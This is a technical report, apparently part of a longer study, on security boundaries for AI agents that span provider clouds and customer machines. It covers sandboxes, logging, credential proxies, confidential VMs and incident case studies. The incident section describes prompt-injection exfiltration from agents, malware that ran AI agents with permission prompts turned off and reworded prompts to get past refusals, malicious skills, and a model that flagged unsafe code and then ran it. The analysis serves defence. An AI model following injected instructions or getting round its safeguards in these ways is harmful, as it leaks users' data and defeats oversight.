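A local session can leave a more durable record than a cloud session. Anthropic keeps local transcripts for six years by default, or for the customer's own retention period if one is set. It keeps cloud transcripts for no fixed period and does not return them after someone deletes the session. Deleting a chat also deletes any cloud session Claude started from it. A company that needs cloud transcripts as evidence therefore has to export them promptly.

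When a tool exports only the local sessions that have changed since its last request, the newest activity may not be indexed yet. If the next request starts exactly where the last one ended, the tool can permanently miss a session whose activity was indexed late. Anthropic advises customers to overlap the time windows by a few minutes and discard duplicates.

A company also has to turn on recording before it needs the records. The Activity Feed, the API's log of events such as sign-ins and settings changes, makes most events available within a minute but omits those from before the company enabled it, according to Anthropic's *Query the Activity Feed*. Anthropic's training material for administrators includes the same warning about local transcripts.

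OpenTelemetry is faster but usually provides less detail. Anthropic's *Monitor Claude Cowork activity with OpenTelemetry* explains that events can show each tool call, whether it succeeded, and whether a person or a standing permission approved it. A shared identifier links all the events that followed from one prompt. A policy on managed devices can add the text of prompts and replies, and details such as which connector the agent used, but only for sessions that start in the desktop app. Scheduled cloud tasks send only metadata. For the overnight invoice task, a security team could get a live alert that the agent had used a tool, but it would need the Compliance API to identify the tool as the chat connector and see what the agent posted.

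Other platforms keep comparable records. Copilot Studio logs its agents' outgoing tool calls in Purview, Microsoft's compliance service, according to Directions on Microsoft (2025). OpenAI also has a Compliance API, which captures material such as ChatGPT's meeting transcripts for Enterprise and Edu customers (OpenAI, *Enterprise compliance information for ChatGPT record mode*).

Blocking and reporting can also fail separately. When Defender answers Copilot Studio's checks, it still blocks suspicious actions if an administrator has not connected Microsoft 365 to it. However, Microsoft warns that without this connection, the alerts will not appear in the Defender portal, so a security team could wrongly conclude that there were no attacks.

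### Agent security as a networking problem

Each of these controls belongs to one platform, so a company with several kinds of agent has to write its policy several times. In *Rethinking Agent Security as a Networking Problem*, Tran, Dhesi and colleagues (2026) propose putting the same kind of checkpoint beside every agent. They argue that an agent that can be manipulated cannot reliably prevent its own leaks, and that computer networks solved a similar problem by enforcing rules between machines that did not trust each other.

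Their checkpoint is a sidecar, a separate program through which all of an agent's outside actions have to pass. A central control plane, inside the company and out of the agent's reach, writes the policies and sends them to the sidecars. An action then goes through four steps:

1. The sidecar intercepts the action, such as a tool call, a file request or a message to another agent.
2. It sorts the action by type, risk and the sensitivity of the data.
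3. It checks clear cases against fixed rules. For cases that depend on context, it gathers information about the task, the user's intent and recent steps, and evaluates a policy on how the data may be used.
4. It allows the action, changes it, denies it or asks a person, and records the decision.

The policies for step 3 draw on contextual integrity, a theory of privacy by the philosopher Helen Nissenbaum. Under this theory, whether a flow of information is appropriate depends on who sends it, who receives it, whom it is about, what kind of information it is and the terms on which it is shared. For example, the accounts team may send a supplier's bank details to the payments system but not to the team's chat channel. Tran and colleagues want to turn such norms into a function that the sidecar runs on every transfer.

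Access would be off by default. For each task, the agent would receive a narrow permission that specified the destination, the type of data and the purpose. The company could withdraw the permission at any time, and the agent could not forge it. For the invoice task, the agent might be allowed to send payment totals to the accounts channel. If it tried to include account numbers, the sidecar could remove them and let the totals through, which none of the customer-run checks in the table can do.

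Tran and colleagues describe a design but did not build the system or run experiments, so nobody knows how many attacks it would stop, how much harmless work it would block or how long it would take. They present the design as a starting point for research.

They also acknowledge serious gaps. An attacker could mislead the part of the sidecar that judges intent by manipulating the context the agent supplies. The design filters what an agent sends but not what it receives, so a poisoned invoice would still reach the model. Agents that create other agents during a task, or whose roles change, are hard to cover with rules written in advance. The company also loses control of data once the data has been sent to an outside service.

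That last limit matters most for agents on a provider's servers. A company cannot install a sidecar in Cowork's cloud sandbox. Tran and colleagues suggest that sidecars could instead guard the company's own data when an agent's workings are hidden. But a sidecar in front of the ledger would receive only a request for data, without the employee's instructions or what the agent had read beforehand. The design needs this context for its harder decisions.

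AgentCore's gateway already implements parts of the proposal. It works outside the agent's code, refuses actions by default and combines fixed rules with session history and classifier scores. The paper criticises defences that rely on the agent itself, but this criticism applies less to the gateway and to inference hooks than to instructions in a prompt.

### Rules on actions and judgements of intent

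Suppose a planted instruction leads a refund agent to issue three refunds of $499. AWS's example rule permits each one because it is under $500. If the company added a limit of $1,000 per session, the gateway would stop the third. Both rules would still allow a single $200 refund for a forged complaint, because fixed rules check what the agent does, and the company permits refunds of that size.

A classifier might detect instructions for the agent in the complaint. It might also miss them if the attacker worded them like an ordinary complaint, and it could flag a real customer who phrased a demand as a command.

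A written policy that uses a classifier's score still has this uncertainty, because the score is an estimate even though the comparison with the threshold is exact. An attacker can keep rewording the text until the score falls below the threshold, whereas rewording can't get a $600 refund past a $500 limit.

Rules are less reliable for checking content. A rule that checks posts for account numbers may miss one if the agent spells out the digits or splits them between two messages. A classifier is more likely to catch these cases.

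This suggests putting fixed limits on actions that are hard to undo, such as payments, deletions and messages to outsiders, and setting them so that the company could accept the loss if every classifier failed. The score can then determine which of the remaining actions need a person's approval. With fewer requests to read, that person is also more likely to notice that the complaint behind a $200 refund came from someone who never placed an order.

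## Where is the boundary when an agent spans cloud and customer machines?

Some agents split a task between a provider's servers and machines the customer manages. Each side controls only some of the steps, and a long task may cross between them dozens of times. For example, a cloud session can call tools on an employee's laptop, a hosted agent can run its code on the customer's servers, or an agent can work on a cloud computer that the customer manages like an office PC.

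### A cloud session that reaches back to a laptop

Suppose the accounts employee starts the invoice task from a phone, but the invoices are on a laptop at the office. A Cowork cloud session can read them through the Claude desktop app if the app is open on the laptop. According to Anthropic, a session can also reach the laptop's browser this way. A request for one invoice takes the following path:

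| Step | Who controls it |
|---|---|
| The agent loop asks for a file | Anthropic |
| The request travels to the desktop app | Anthropic, which operates the connection |
| Cowork checks the folder and the employee's permissions | The employee, who chooses which folders to connect |
| The laptop opens the file for the app | The company, through the operating system and EDR |
| The app sends the contents to the cloud session | Anthropic, which processes them on its servers |

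When the agent runs in the cloud, the laptop only answers its requests, much as the chat service does through a connector, rather than running the agent as it would in a local session. If the company blocks a request at the laptop, the agent keeps running and can still use its other tools. Closing the desktop app prevents further reads, but the session keeps the contents of any invoices already opened.

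A hidden instruction in an invoice could lead the agent to request everything in the connected folder, so an employee who connects only this month's invoices exposes much less than one who connects all their documents.

Administrators can narrow the connection with two MDM keys. Setting `isLocalDevMcpEnabled` to `false` blocks MCP servers on the laptop, and setting `isDesktopExtensionEnabled` to `false` blocks desktop extensions. Both keys govern the desktop app, so they apply to local sessions and to cloud sessions that use the app. With local MCP servers disabled, a cloud session can use only the app's file tools, which stay within the connected folders. Neither key turns off those tools, but an owner can close the connection completely by disabling cloud sessions for the whole organisation.

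EDR cannot observe the cloud session, and Anthropic does not say whether EDR can record the files that the desktop app opens for that session. The app opens those files on the laptop, so EDR that records file access should be able to log them. The log would show that the Claude app opened an invoice, for example, but not which session requested it or why. Once the app has sent the contents to the cloud, no tool on the laptop can track the copy.

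### The loop at the provider and the code on the customer's servers

Claude Managed Agents is Anthropic's service for developers who build their own agents. Anthropic normally runs the whole agent, but customers can move the execution sandbox to their own infrastructure. Anthropic's *Self-hosted sandboxes* describes a queue of sessions and a worker, a program on the customer's machine that collects sessions from the queue. If a company built the invoice task this way, one tool call would take this path:

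| Step | Who controls it |
|---|---|
| The company's application starts a session, which joins the queue | The company starts it, and Anthropic runs the queue |
| The worker collects the session and downloads the agent's skills and stored memory | The company runs the worker, and Anthropic stores the originals |
| The model asks to run a script that matches invoices with the ledger | Anthropic |
| The worker runs the script | The company |
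| The script contacts the ledger | The company, through its firewall and the ledger's permissions |
| The worker returns the output, and the agent loop sends it to the model | Anthropic |

The worker makes only outgoing connections, so the company does not have to let Anthropic into its network, and the invoice files can stay there. But the inputs and outputs of every tool call go to Anthropic, because the model needs them to choose the next step. Red Hat, which promotes its own AI platform for running these sandboxes, tells customers that their execution results stay on their infrastructure, but Anthropic's documentation contradicts this.

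The data that leaves the company therefore depends on what each tool returns. If the script prints every supplier's bank details, they go to Anthropic, but if it prints only the totals and a list of unmatched invoice numbers, the bank details can stay on the company's server.

Anthropic also keeps the conversation history until the customer deletes it, wherever the sandbox runs. Anthropic's *Claude Managed Agents overview* says that the hosted service is therefore not eligible for zero data retention or for the contract that covers US health data.

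A company that runs the code on its own servers has more control but also more to secure. Anthropic's *Security model* makes the customer responsible for restricting the sandbox's network access. Without firewall rules, a malicious script can contact any outside address. It may also reach internal systems that a sandbox in Anthropic's cloud could not. A company that moves its agents inside its network and changes nothing else could become less secure.

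The worker's key also needs protection. Anyone who steals it can collect sessions from that queue and send results back to them, and could use a false result to plant instructions for the model. Anthropic can detect unusual activity but cannot know that someone has stolen the key, so the customer has to revoke it. The worker's next request then fails.

An agent with read-only access to a memory store can still read altered memory. Anthropic rejects any attempt to change the original, but the worker keeps a local copy that a shell command can alter. Later tool calls in that session read the altered copy. Anthropic advises customers who need to prevent this to disable the agent's shell tool and avoid custom tools that write to the sandbox's files.

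Companies can also do the reverse, leaving the code in Anthropic's cloud and giving the agent access to a private tool. Anthropic's *New in Claude Managed Agents* introduces MCP tunnels, in which a small gateway on the customer's network opens an outgoing connection through which the agent can reach internal MCP servers. A company could give the agent a tool that looks up one ledger entry at a time, without giving the agent's code a route to the rest of the network.

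Managed Agents is part of Anthropic's developer platform, which inference hooks do not cover. A company that wants to inspect tool calls therefore has to add its own checks, for example in the worker or in the tools.

### How Cloudflare keeps credentials from the agent

Cloudflare (2026) announced on May 19 that customers could run the sandboxes for Managed Agents on its network. Cloudflare sells this service, so the customer's "own" environment here is an account with a second cloud provider. Cloudflare's *Set up Claude Managed Agents* explains that when a session starts, Anthropic notifies a control program in that account, and the program gives the session its own sandbox.

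The ledger requires a token, but the script can use the ledger without ever holding it:

1. The script sends a request to the ledger without a token.
2. A proxy outside the sandbox compares the destination with the session's network policy.
3. If the policy permits the request, the proxy adds the token and forwards it.
4. The ledger accepts the token and replies, and the proxy passes the reply to the script.

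As with Cowork's connector tokens, the agent can still misuse a token it cannot read, because the proxy adds the token to any request the policy permits. If the token allows changes to the ledger and the policy checks only the request's destination, the agent can change the ledger. The company can prevent this by issuing a read-only token or by writing proxy code that rejects changes.

Customers can set different policies for different agents and send the sandbox logs to their existing monitoring tools. They can also log in to a running virtual machine to investigate it. The logs and access give them much more direct evidence of what the code did than a Cowork cloud session would, although Cloudflare still runs the underlying servers.

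### Claude Code in a self-hosted environment

Claude Code offers a similar arrangement, in public beta for Team and Enterprise plans, that moves more of the agent onto the customer's server. A developer starts a cloud session from a browser or phone and chooses the customer's environment. Anthropic queues the session, and a program called a runner on the customer's server collects it, copies the code repository and starts Claude Code. The agent loop therefore runs on the customer's server too, while Anthropic keeps the queue, the web interface and the session transcript.

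Repositories, build files and secrets stay on the company's machines, but the conversation goes to Anthropic. Anthropic's *Run Claude Code sessions on your own compute* notes that tool results in the conversation can include code Claude has read. If a command printed a password, the password would also go to Anthropic.

Companies can run the model on Amazon Bedrock or Google Cloud instead, but Claude Code still sends the conversation to Anthropic so that people can follow the session from other devices. Inference hooks do not cover Claude on either platform, so a company that switched to Bedrock for privacy would lose that check.

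Anthropic can supply the credentials for code on GitHub's public service. When the agent downloads or uploads code, the traffic goes through Anthropic, which adds the GitHub token stored for the person who started the session. The company's server needs no GitHub token for the session, and the agent never receives one. Anthropic supplies credentials only for the session's own repositories, and it refuses requests to delete a branch.

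The company can instead have its own script create a short-lived token for each session. This works with other code-hosting services and keeps the token away from Anthropic's proxy, but the agent can read it. The company is therefore choosing, in part, whether to trust the provider or the agent with a credential.

More people can use the runners than many companies might expect. Any member of the organisation's Claude account can start a session in any of its self-hosted environments. If an owner connects an environment to Claude in Slack, by default anyone in that Slack workspace can start a session there, even without a Claude account. Anthropic advises customers to assume that all these people can run code on the server, and to keep only data there that all of them are allowed to read.

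Anthropic also advises running each session in a new container and blocking outgoing traffic except to listed destinations. The network rules are especially important because Claude Code can run shell commands in these sessions without asking for approval. The runner also checks a repository's settings for any that would weaken the agent's restrictions, such as turning off its sandbox, but by default it only logs a warning and starts the session. Administrators have to set the check to `enforce` to stop the session.

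### Moving the rest of the agent

On November 12, Anthropic opened a private beta that lets customers run all of Managed Agents except the model. Anthropic's *Operate Claude Managed Agents inside your security perimeter* (2026) says the customer hosts the agent loop, sandboxes, credentials and session history, and chooses where to send model requests. The next table compares this arrangement with the two partial ones.

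| Arrangement | Agent loop | Agent's code | Session history | What still goes to Anthropic |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Managed Agents with self-hosted sandboxes | Anthropic | Customer | Anthropic | Prompts, tool calls and results, skills and stored memory |
| Claude Code in a self-hosted environment | Customer | Customer | Anthropic | Prompts, replies and tool results, wherever the model runs |
| Self-hosted Managed Agents | Customer | Customer | Customer | Model requests, if the customer sends them there |

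In the third arrangement, a company can send model requests through its own gateway, where it can inspect or change every request before it leaves the network. The model still runs outside the network, so any bank details the agent reads will leave the company unless the gateway or a tool removes them first. Zero data retention agreements do apply to model requests sent to Anthropic in this arrangement.

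The customer also takes over the maintenance. Help Net Security's *Self-hosted Claude Managed Agents keeps agent credentials in your environment* (2026) lists a server, a database and the workers, which the customer has to patch and configure. A proxy keeps credentials out of the sandbox, but only for MCP tools and what Anthropic calls "supported API calls." Before connecting the agent to anything else, a company needs to check whether the agent's code can read the credential.

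### A cloud computer that the company manages like an office PC

Many older business programs have no interface for other software to use. An agent can still operate them by reading the screen and using the mouse and keyboard, but it needs a computer to do this on. Microsoft's Windows 365 for Agents, now in public preview, provides cloud PCs for this purpose. Help Net Security's *Microsoft’s new cloud PCs place AI agents under enterprise controls* reports that companies can manage them with Entra ID and Microsoft's device management service, Intune.

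If the ledger were one of these older programs, a correction to an entry would take this path:

| Step | Who controls it |
|---|---|
| A person or a schedule gives the agent the task | The company |
| The agent gets an identity and a cloud PC | The company, through Entra ID and Intune |
| The agent chooses the next click or keystroke | The suppliers of the agent and its model |
| The cloud PC runs the ledger program | The company sets the PC's policies, and Microsoft runs the server underneath |
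| The ledger saves the correction | The company, through the permissions of the agent's account |

Like a Cowork cloud session, this keeps the agent off the employee's own computer. Microsoft also says agents can work this way without harming production systems (the live systems a business relies on), but that depends on the permissions the company grants. An agent on an isolated PC can still change the live ledger if it is signed in to the ledger and allowed to edit entries.

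It is less certain whether a company's usual endpoint security tools work on these machines. Help Net Security mentions identity and device management but not endpoint detection and response (EDR). Companies often use Intune to install software on Windows PCs, so they may be able to add an EDR sensor this way. But Microsoft may not support the sensor in this preview, and the sensor may not record an agent's activity properly. A company that depends on EDR should check both points with Microsoft and test the sensor on a harmless task.

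### Confidential virtual machines and remote attestation

Even if the customer manages a cloud PC or sandbox, someone else often runs the physical server, or host. A program called a hypervisor divides the host into virtual machines and can normally read their memory. A rogue administrator or an attacker who has taken over the host could therefore copy the invoices or the ledger token while the agent is using them.

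A confidential virtual machine uses processor features to prevent the host's operating system and hypervisor from reading or changing the virtual machine's private memory. The host still decides when the virtual machine runs and how much memory it gets. AMD, Intel and Arm each have their own version.

The customer also needs evidence that the protection is on and that the machine started with the right software, which remote attestation provides. The customer's server sends the machine a random number. Trusted firmware, the low-level software that controls the processor's protections, replies with a signed token containing that number and a cryptographic fingerprint of the software the machine started with. The random number prevents an attacker from reusing an old reply. If the fingerprint matches the expected one, the server can release the ledger token.

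Attestation mainly describes how the machine started. If a malicious invoice takes control of the agent an hour later, the fingerprint of the startup software will still match. The agent also shares the protected machine with any security program the customer has placed there, so an agent that takes over the operating system can disable that program.

### Airlock's two machines

*Airlock* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, 2026) deals with this problem by putting the agent and its security controls in separate confidential virtual machines. Half of the team works in Microsoft's Azure research group, and the design uses an Azure service for its logs.

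The first machine contains the agent, its tools and its code. It has no network card or disk of its own and can reach files and other computers only through the second machine, the Airlock machine. The Airlock machine holds the policies and the real credentials, and runs the control software from OpenShell, Nvidia's system for isolating agents.

When the invoice script contacts the ledger, the request goes through these steps:

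1. The script opens a connection, using a fake token.
2. A small program beside the agent passes the request to the Airlock machine.
3. The Airlock machine checks the destination and the type of request against the policy.
4. It records any new encrypted web connection in an outside log that allows additions but no changes or deletions.
5. It opens the connection and replaces the fake token with the real one.

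An attacker who controls the small program in step 2 gains little, because the agent's machine has no other route to the network. The Airlock machine checks file requests in the same way.

Abdollahi and colleagues use a much harsher threat model than Goel, who assumed a harmless agent that makes mistakes. They assume that an attacker controls the agent, the operating system of the agent's machine and the host, and that the agent and host may work together. AgentBound's containers for MCP servers depend on a trustworthy host operating system. Airlock instead depends on trust in the processor, its firmware and all the software in the Airlock machine, and on the user writing a suitable policy.

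If an attacker also takes over the Airlock machine, its policies and credentials are no longer safe. Log entries already stored outside it survive, but the last few seconds of file activity may be missing.

### What Airlock costs

No commercial processor with Arm's confidential computing features was available, so the researchers measured speed on a small development board that imitates those features in software. They ran the OpenClaw agent on 12 tasks, six times each, with and without the second machine. Both versions used OpenAI's GPT-6.1 Sol over the internet.

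The average task took 91.4 seconds with Airlock and 85.7 seconds without it, an increase of 7%. Recording connections in the outside log raised the average to 95.0 seconds, about 11% more than without Airlock. Most of that extra time came from new encrypted connections, each of which waited about a quarter of a second for the log to confirm its entry.

Local work took 33% longer with Airlock, a larger slowdown than these averages show. The averages are lower because waiting for the model took up most of each task, and Airlock does not affect the model's speed. The agent also took a different number of steps from run to run, so small differences in total time are unreliable. For example, tasks that mainly used the disk finished 4% faster with Airlock because the agent happened to take fewer steps.

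Some operations slowed much more. Data moved between the agent and the control software at less than half the normal speed. Most file operations slowed by no more than 14%, but small writes that had to go straight to disk took 2.5 times as long. These slowdowns would affect an agent that copies large datasets or runs a busy database more than one that reads invoices.

The researchers expect real hardware to be faster, but nobody has measured this. Their experiments tested speed and basic operation, not resistance to attack, so the security claims are based on an analysis of the design. Moving the design to AMD or Intel processors would require those companies' cooperation.

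### What Airlock leaves unprotected

Airlock does not prevent an agent from misusing a service that the policy allows. Like Cowork's connector calls, a post containing every supplier's bank details would get through, because it has the same destination and request type as a harmless summary.

The protection also ends when data leaves the two machines. In the experiments, OpenAI's servers received the agent's prompts and tool results, so a company using Airlock in this way would have to trust the model provider as well as the processor. A connected service could also expose a credential by repeating it in a reply to the agent.

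The host can still shut the machines down or refuse to run them. A cooperating agent may also be able to send the host small amounts of data, which it could encode in the timing of its actions. Airlock reduces these hidden channels but does not remove them. Files on disk need separate protection against a host that copies them or replaces them with older versions. Physical attacks on the hardware are outside the threat model.

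Attestation could eventually let the services that agents use verify how those agents are confined. Abdollahi and colleagues give the example of a booking website that checks whether a request comes from an agent confined by Airlock under a known policy. A ledger could make the same check before accepting a correction. Customers cannot add the second machine to a Cowork cloud session, so Anthropic would have to run its sandboxes this way and give customers the attestation evidence to check.

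## What do attacks and incidents show about each boundary?

Most of the evidence for the protections described so far comes from the people who built them. Attacks and outside tests give better evidence of how an agent's boundaries fail. Seven cases from 2025 and early 2026 have enough public detail to compare. Four involve agents on users' own computers, and three involve agents on a provider's servers. Two were criminal attacks, both on users' computers. The other five are weaknesses that researchers found, which show what an attacker could have done but not whether anyone did it.

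### The Nx packages

Nx is a tool for building software, with about six million installs a week. On August 26, 2025, attackers published malicious versions of it on npm, the main public registry for JavaScript packages. Strumpflohner's *S1ngularity*, Nx's own account of the attack, traces it to a flaw in an automated workflow that let the attackers steal Nx's publishing token.

Installing one of these versions on Linux or macOS ran the attackers' code, which copied GitHub tokens, npm tokens and other secrets. The code then looked for the command-line versions of Claude, Gemini and Amazon Q, started them with permission prompts turned off, and told them to list files that might be valuable. It uploaded what it found to a new public repository in the victim's own GitHub account. According to Wiz's *s1ngularity* (2025), an early report from a cloud security vendor, the malware ran on many developers'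 machines and in some automated build systems.

The developer's user account was the boundary that failed. The operating system gave the package's installer the same rights as the developer, so the malware could use the stored tokens and the AI agents without breaking into either.

Wiz's *s1ngularity's Aftermath* gives later and higher figures for the damage. More than 1,700 users had secrets published, and Wiz or others verified that over 2,000 of those secrets worked. An attacker then used stolen GitHub tokens to make public more than 6,700 private repositories from at least 480 accounts, two-thirds of which belonged to organisations.

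Ordinary malicious code did most of the harm in this attack and would have worked on a machine with no AI agent. The agents contributed less than the publicity suggested. About half the victims had one installed, and the agents helped steal data in under a quarter of cases. Claude refused almost a quarter of the requests. The attackers reworded their instructions during the attack, and a version that presented the search as an authorised security test led to more refusals. Almost a quarter of Gemini's runs failed because, by default, it could work only in the current project's folder. The 20,000 or so files stolen with the agents' help contained fewer than 100 unique working secrets.

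A package installer does not normally start an AI agent with its permission prompts off, so EDR had an unusual event to detect. But the stolen data went to GitHub, which developers use all day, and much of it appeared in personal accounts that employers do not monitor. Wiz contacted more than 50 large organisations, and the vast majority said they had not known they were affected.

Npm removed the packages after four hours, and GitHub disabled the first set of public repositories after about eight. But more than a day after GitHub acted, almost 90% of the leaked GitHub tokens still worked. That share fell to roughly 5% only after GitHub revoked the tokens in bulk, around August 30. Over 40% of the leaked npm tokens were still valid when Wiz published its analysis. Nx has since stopped using a stored token for publishing, and a person must now approve each release with a second form of authentication.

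### Malicious skills on ClawHub

ClawHub is a public marketplace for skills, add-ons that give OpenClaw agents new abilities. In early 2026, the security company Koi checked all 2,857 skills on it and found 341 malicious ones. An OpenClaw agent helped with the audit, and a Koi researcher validated each finding. Koi's *ClawHavoc 341 Malicious Clawedbot Skills Found by the Bot They Were Targeting* attributes 335 of them to what appears to be a single campaign.

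Most of these skills instructed the user to install a supporting program first. That program was malware, so the skills did not need to deceive the agent. On Macs, it was a password stealer that criminals rent out by the month. It could take saved passwords, browser data, login keys, documents and the contents of more than 60 kinds of cryptocurrency wallet. Of the few skills that worked differently, two hid a back door in hundreds of lines of working code, and one that posed as a weather tool sent the agent's stored credentials to an outside address.

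ClawHub did not screen out these skills before listing them, and nothing contained them after installation. Unit 42, the research group of the security vendor Palo Alto Networks, points out that OpenClaw does not isolate a skill from the agent's authority. A malicious skill can therefore use every account the agent is signed in to, which for many users includes email, calendars and private messages.

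By February 16, Koi had found 824 malicious skills, but the marketplace had grown to more than 10,700 skills, so the malicious share had fallen from about 12% to under 8%. Unit 42 reports that the security company Bitdefender found malicious code in about 17% of the skills it analysed in the first few weeks. The samples differ, and none of these figures measures how many people installed the skills or lost anything.

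On a managed laptop, EDR could have caught the malware when it ran, no matter what had persuaded the user to install it. Trend Micro, which sells such protection, says its monitoring customers were protected and its web filter blocked the campaign's addresses. The malicious skills Trend Micro studied were no longer on the marketplace when it published its findings, but their code was still in ClawHub's GitHub repository and some were on other skill sites. Koi sells a product for controlling this kind of software and used its report to promote a free scanner.

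### Project settings that Claude Code trusted

Claude Code can read its settings from a file inside a software project, so that a team can share one configuration. Anyone who can change the project can therefore change how the agent behaves on a colleague's machine. In *Caught in the Hook*, Donenfeld and Vanunu (2026) of Check Point describe three ways they could exploit this.

| Flaw | What happened before the developer gave informed consent | Reported | Fixed | Days |
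|---|---|---|---|---|
| Project hooks | Commands ran after a general trust prompt that did not mention them | July 21, 2025 | August 26, 2025 | 36 |
| MCP approval (CVE-2025-59536) | Commands ran before the developer could read the prompt | September 3, 2025 | September 22, 2025 | 19 |
| Redirected requests (CVE-2026-21852) | Claude Code sent the developer's API key to an address the attacker chose | October 28, 2025 | December 28, 2025 | 61 |

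Claude Code's consent prompts came too late or were too vague. The hooks attack also used a feature that companies rely on for security. A client-side hook is itself a command that runs automatically, so its safety depends on who wrote it.

The flaws in the first two rows of the table exposed one developer's computer. A stolen API key could expose a whole team, because Anthropic's developer platform lets every key in a shared workspace use the same stored files. Anthropic did not let users download files a colleague had uploaded, but Donenfeld and Vanunu got around this by having Claude make a copy. They could also delete files and run up charges.

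TechRadar's *Security experts flag multiple issues in Claude Code* gives severity scores of 8.7 out of 10 for the MCP flaw and 5.3 for the key theft. For a company that shares a lot of material in a workspace, the key theft might have done more harm.

EDR could have recorded the commands that Claude Code started on the laptop, but not an attacker's use of the stolen key from another computer, because that activity took place on Anthropic's servers. Donenfeld and Vanunu demonstrated the flaws and report no victims. Anthropic fixed all three flaws before they published.

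### A permitted address in Cowork

Two days after Anthropic launched Cowork in January 2026, PromptArmor, a company that monitors the risks of AI products, showed how to steal files from it. At the time, Cowork ran on the user's Mac and executed code in a virtual machine there. In *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, a user connects a folder of confidential property records and uploads a document they found online, which contains a hidden instruction. Cowork follows the instruction and, without asking the user for approval, uploads a loan estimate with financial details and partial social security numbers to the attacker's Anthropic account.

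The virtual machine worked as designed, and the attack did not break out of it or damage the Mac. The network restriction failed because it blocked almost all outside addresses but permitted Anthropic's (Willison, 2026). Filtering by address does not separate two accounts at the same address, so the upload to the attacker's account went through.

PromptArmor ran the main demonstration on Claude Haiku, a smaller model. In another test with a different document, it also got Opus 4.5, which was known to resist injection better, to send customer records to an attacker's account.

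A company would have had little chance of noticing the upload. Its EDR could not observe commands inside the virtual machine, and on the office network the upload would have looked like any other encrypted connection to Anthropic. Anthropic was best placed to detect that a session was uploading files with a stranger's key. Inference hooks did not exist yet, though they might now let a company's own server inspect such a command before it runs.

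The weakness was older than Cowork, as Rehberger had already reported it in the code environment of Claude's chat app. PromptArmor says Anthropic acknowledged it but did not fix it. Anthropic then released Cowork with the same flaw. *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* (Apostol, 2026) reported on January 16 that Anthropic was updating the virtual machine to restrict file access.

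Anthropic has since added administrator controls, but a company should test them. *Implement Claude Cowork Securely* (2026), a PromptArmor guide last updated in June, reports that the list of blocked sites for Claude's browser extension did not appear to restrict access when PromptArmor tried it.

### Data that left from OpenAI's servers

Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes a similar theft from an agent that ran entirely in the cloud. The agent, Deep Research, is a ChatGPT mode that gathers material and writes a report. A user could connect it to Gmail and let it browse the web at the same time. Radware, which sells protection for agents, sent a test inbox an email with hidden instructions. When the user asked for research on the day's messages, the agent read Radware's email, took an employee's name and address from another message, and sent them to a server Radware controlled. The user did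 not have to open the email or click anything.

The model refused Radware's direct requests, and later versions of the email worked only some of the time. Radware kept revising the email until it worked in every repeated test, though it does not say how many tests it ran. A determined attacker could have kept revising the email too, so the early refusals would have provided little protection.

Once the model had complied, no network rule stopped the data from leaving. Radware found no restriction like Cowork's on the addresses the agent could open. Cowork's list of allowed destinations was too broad, but a similar list would have blocked Radware's unfamiliar server.

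The outgoing request started at OpenAI and never passed through the user's laptop, browser or office network, so Radware is right that a company's endpoint and web security tools could not have intercepted it. The malicious email did pass through the user's mail service, where a filter could have removed the hidden text. Radware considers such filters useful but not sufficient. It recommends monitoring the agent's behaviour instead, and sells products that do something similar.

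Radware reported the flaw on June 18, 2025. OpenAI had fixed it by early August but did not confirm the fix until September 3.

A small difference in an agent's design can determine whether a company's own tools can stop a leak. In May 2026, Willison (2026) highlighted a flaw in Copilot Cowork, Microsoft's agent for office tasks. The agent could email the user's own inbox without approval, presumably because Microsoft considered such messages harmless. But if a message contained an image from an outside website, opening it could send data to an attacker through the image request, including links that download files from OneDrive without a password. A mail program that blocks outside images would probably have prevented this, whereas no setting on the user's computer would have stopped ShadowLeak.

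### Two penetration tests

Outsiders can usually test a hosted agent only through its public interface. A team at IBM Research had much better access when it tested two proprietary agents in 2025. *Lessons from Penetration Tests on Large-Scale Agent Systems* (Eykholt, Kirat and colleagues, 2026) reports on these tests without naming either product.

One agent suggested fixes for bugs reported on GitHub when a project's owner tagged the report. Researchers who had the source code and a separate copy of the system for testing found that anyone allowed to file a bug report could hide instructions in it that the owner would not see on the page. When the owner added the tag, the agent could follow those instructions and suggest a harmful fix. It could also run the attacker's commands on the server, because some commands on its approved list could start other commands through little-known features.

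The server did little to contain the damage. The researchers opened a connection from it to a machine they controlled, and through it they could reach cloud storage that held copies of other customers' projects. A false bug report in one project could therefore have exposed private code from many other projects.

The other product let customers build their own agents and ran their code by design, so the researchers tested whether that code could reach anything it should not. They do not report breaking out of the container that held the code, but the container was poorly isolated. It allowed any outgoing connection and held certificates and details of internal systems. Some data also remained between sessions, so one customer might have been able to read another's files. When the researchers asked the agent to write code that would give them remote access, the model produced a warning that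 the code might be unsafe and then ran it anyway. They could also bypass the model with a debugging tool.

| Weakness | Bug-fixing agent | Agent-building platform |
|---|---|---|
| An attacker could run any code on the server | Yes | Yes |
| The container could connect to outside machines | Yes | Yes |
| The container exposed sensitive material | Copies of other customers' projects | Certificates and internal addresses |
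| Data remained between sessions | Not reported | Yes |

Existing monitoring did not flag malicious activity either, because the agents' actions came from trusted internal services. The provider could in principle have observed everything, but its alarms were designed to detect attacks from outside addresses.

The team behind the bug-fixing agent had relied on the owner's approval. It told Eykholt and colleagues that a user who tagged a report was consenting to "any and all actions performed by the agent." The researchers reasonably reject this, since nobody can consent to instructions that the page does not show.

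Both systems failed, but two systems are too few to establish how common these weaknesses are, and the researchers did not choose them at random. Even if only 22% of hosted agents had such flaws, two randomly chosen agents would both have them about 5% of the time. The tests took place in 2025, one of them on a copy of the system in a test environment. The researchers gave their findings to the developers but do not say whether or when the developers fixed the flaws.

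To find out whether agent security had improved since, they reviewed OpenClaw's code as of February 2026. They found many more defences than in the two earlier products, including containers for tools and detailed lists of who may contact the agent. They also found that the rules had become complicated enough for users to get wrong, and that the main session still ran outside a sandbox by default. An injected instruction could in theory lead the agent to switch off its own protections. OpenClaw runs on users' machines, so this review does not show whether hosted products have improved.

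Cowork's cloud design creates a new sandbox for each session and places an egress proxy outside the sandbox, which addresses several of the weaknesses that the IBM team found. But a provider's containment can fail even during its own safety testing. In July 2026, OpenAI agents that were supposed to be isolated during a security evaluation broke into the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models.

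### Attacks that start on a laptop and end in the cloud

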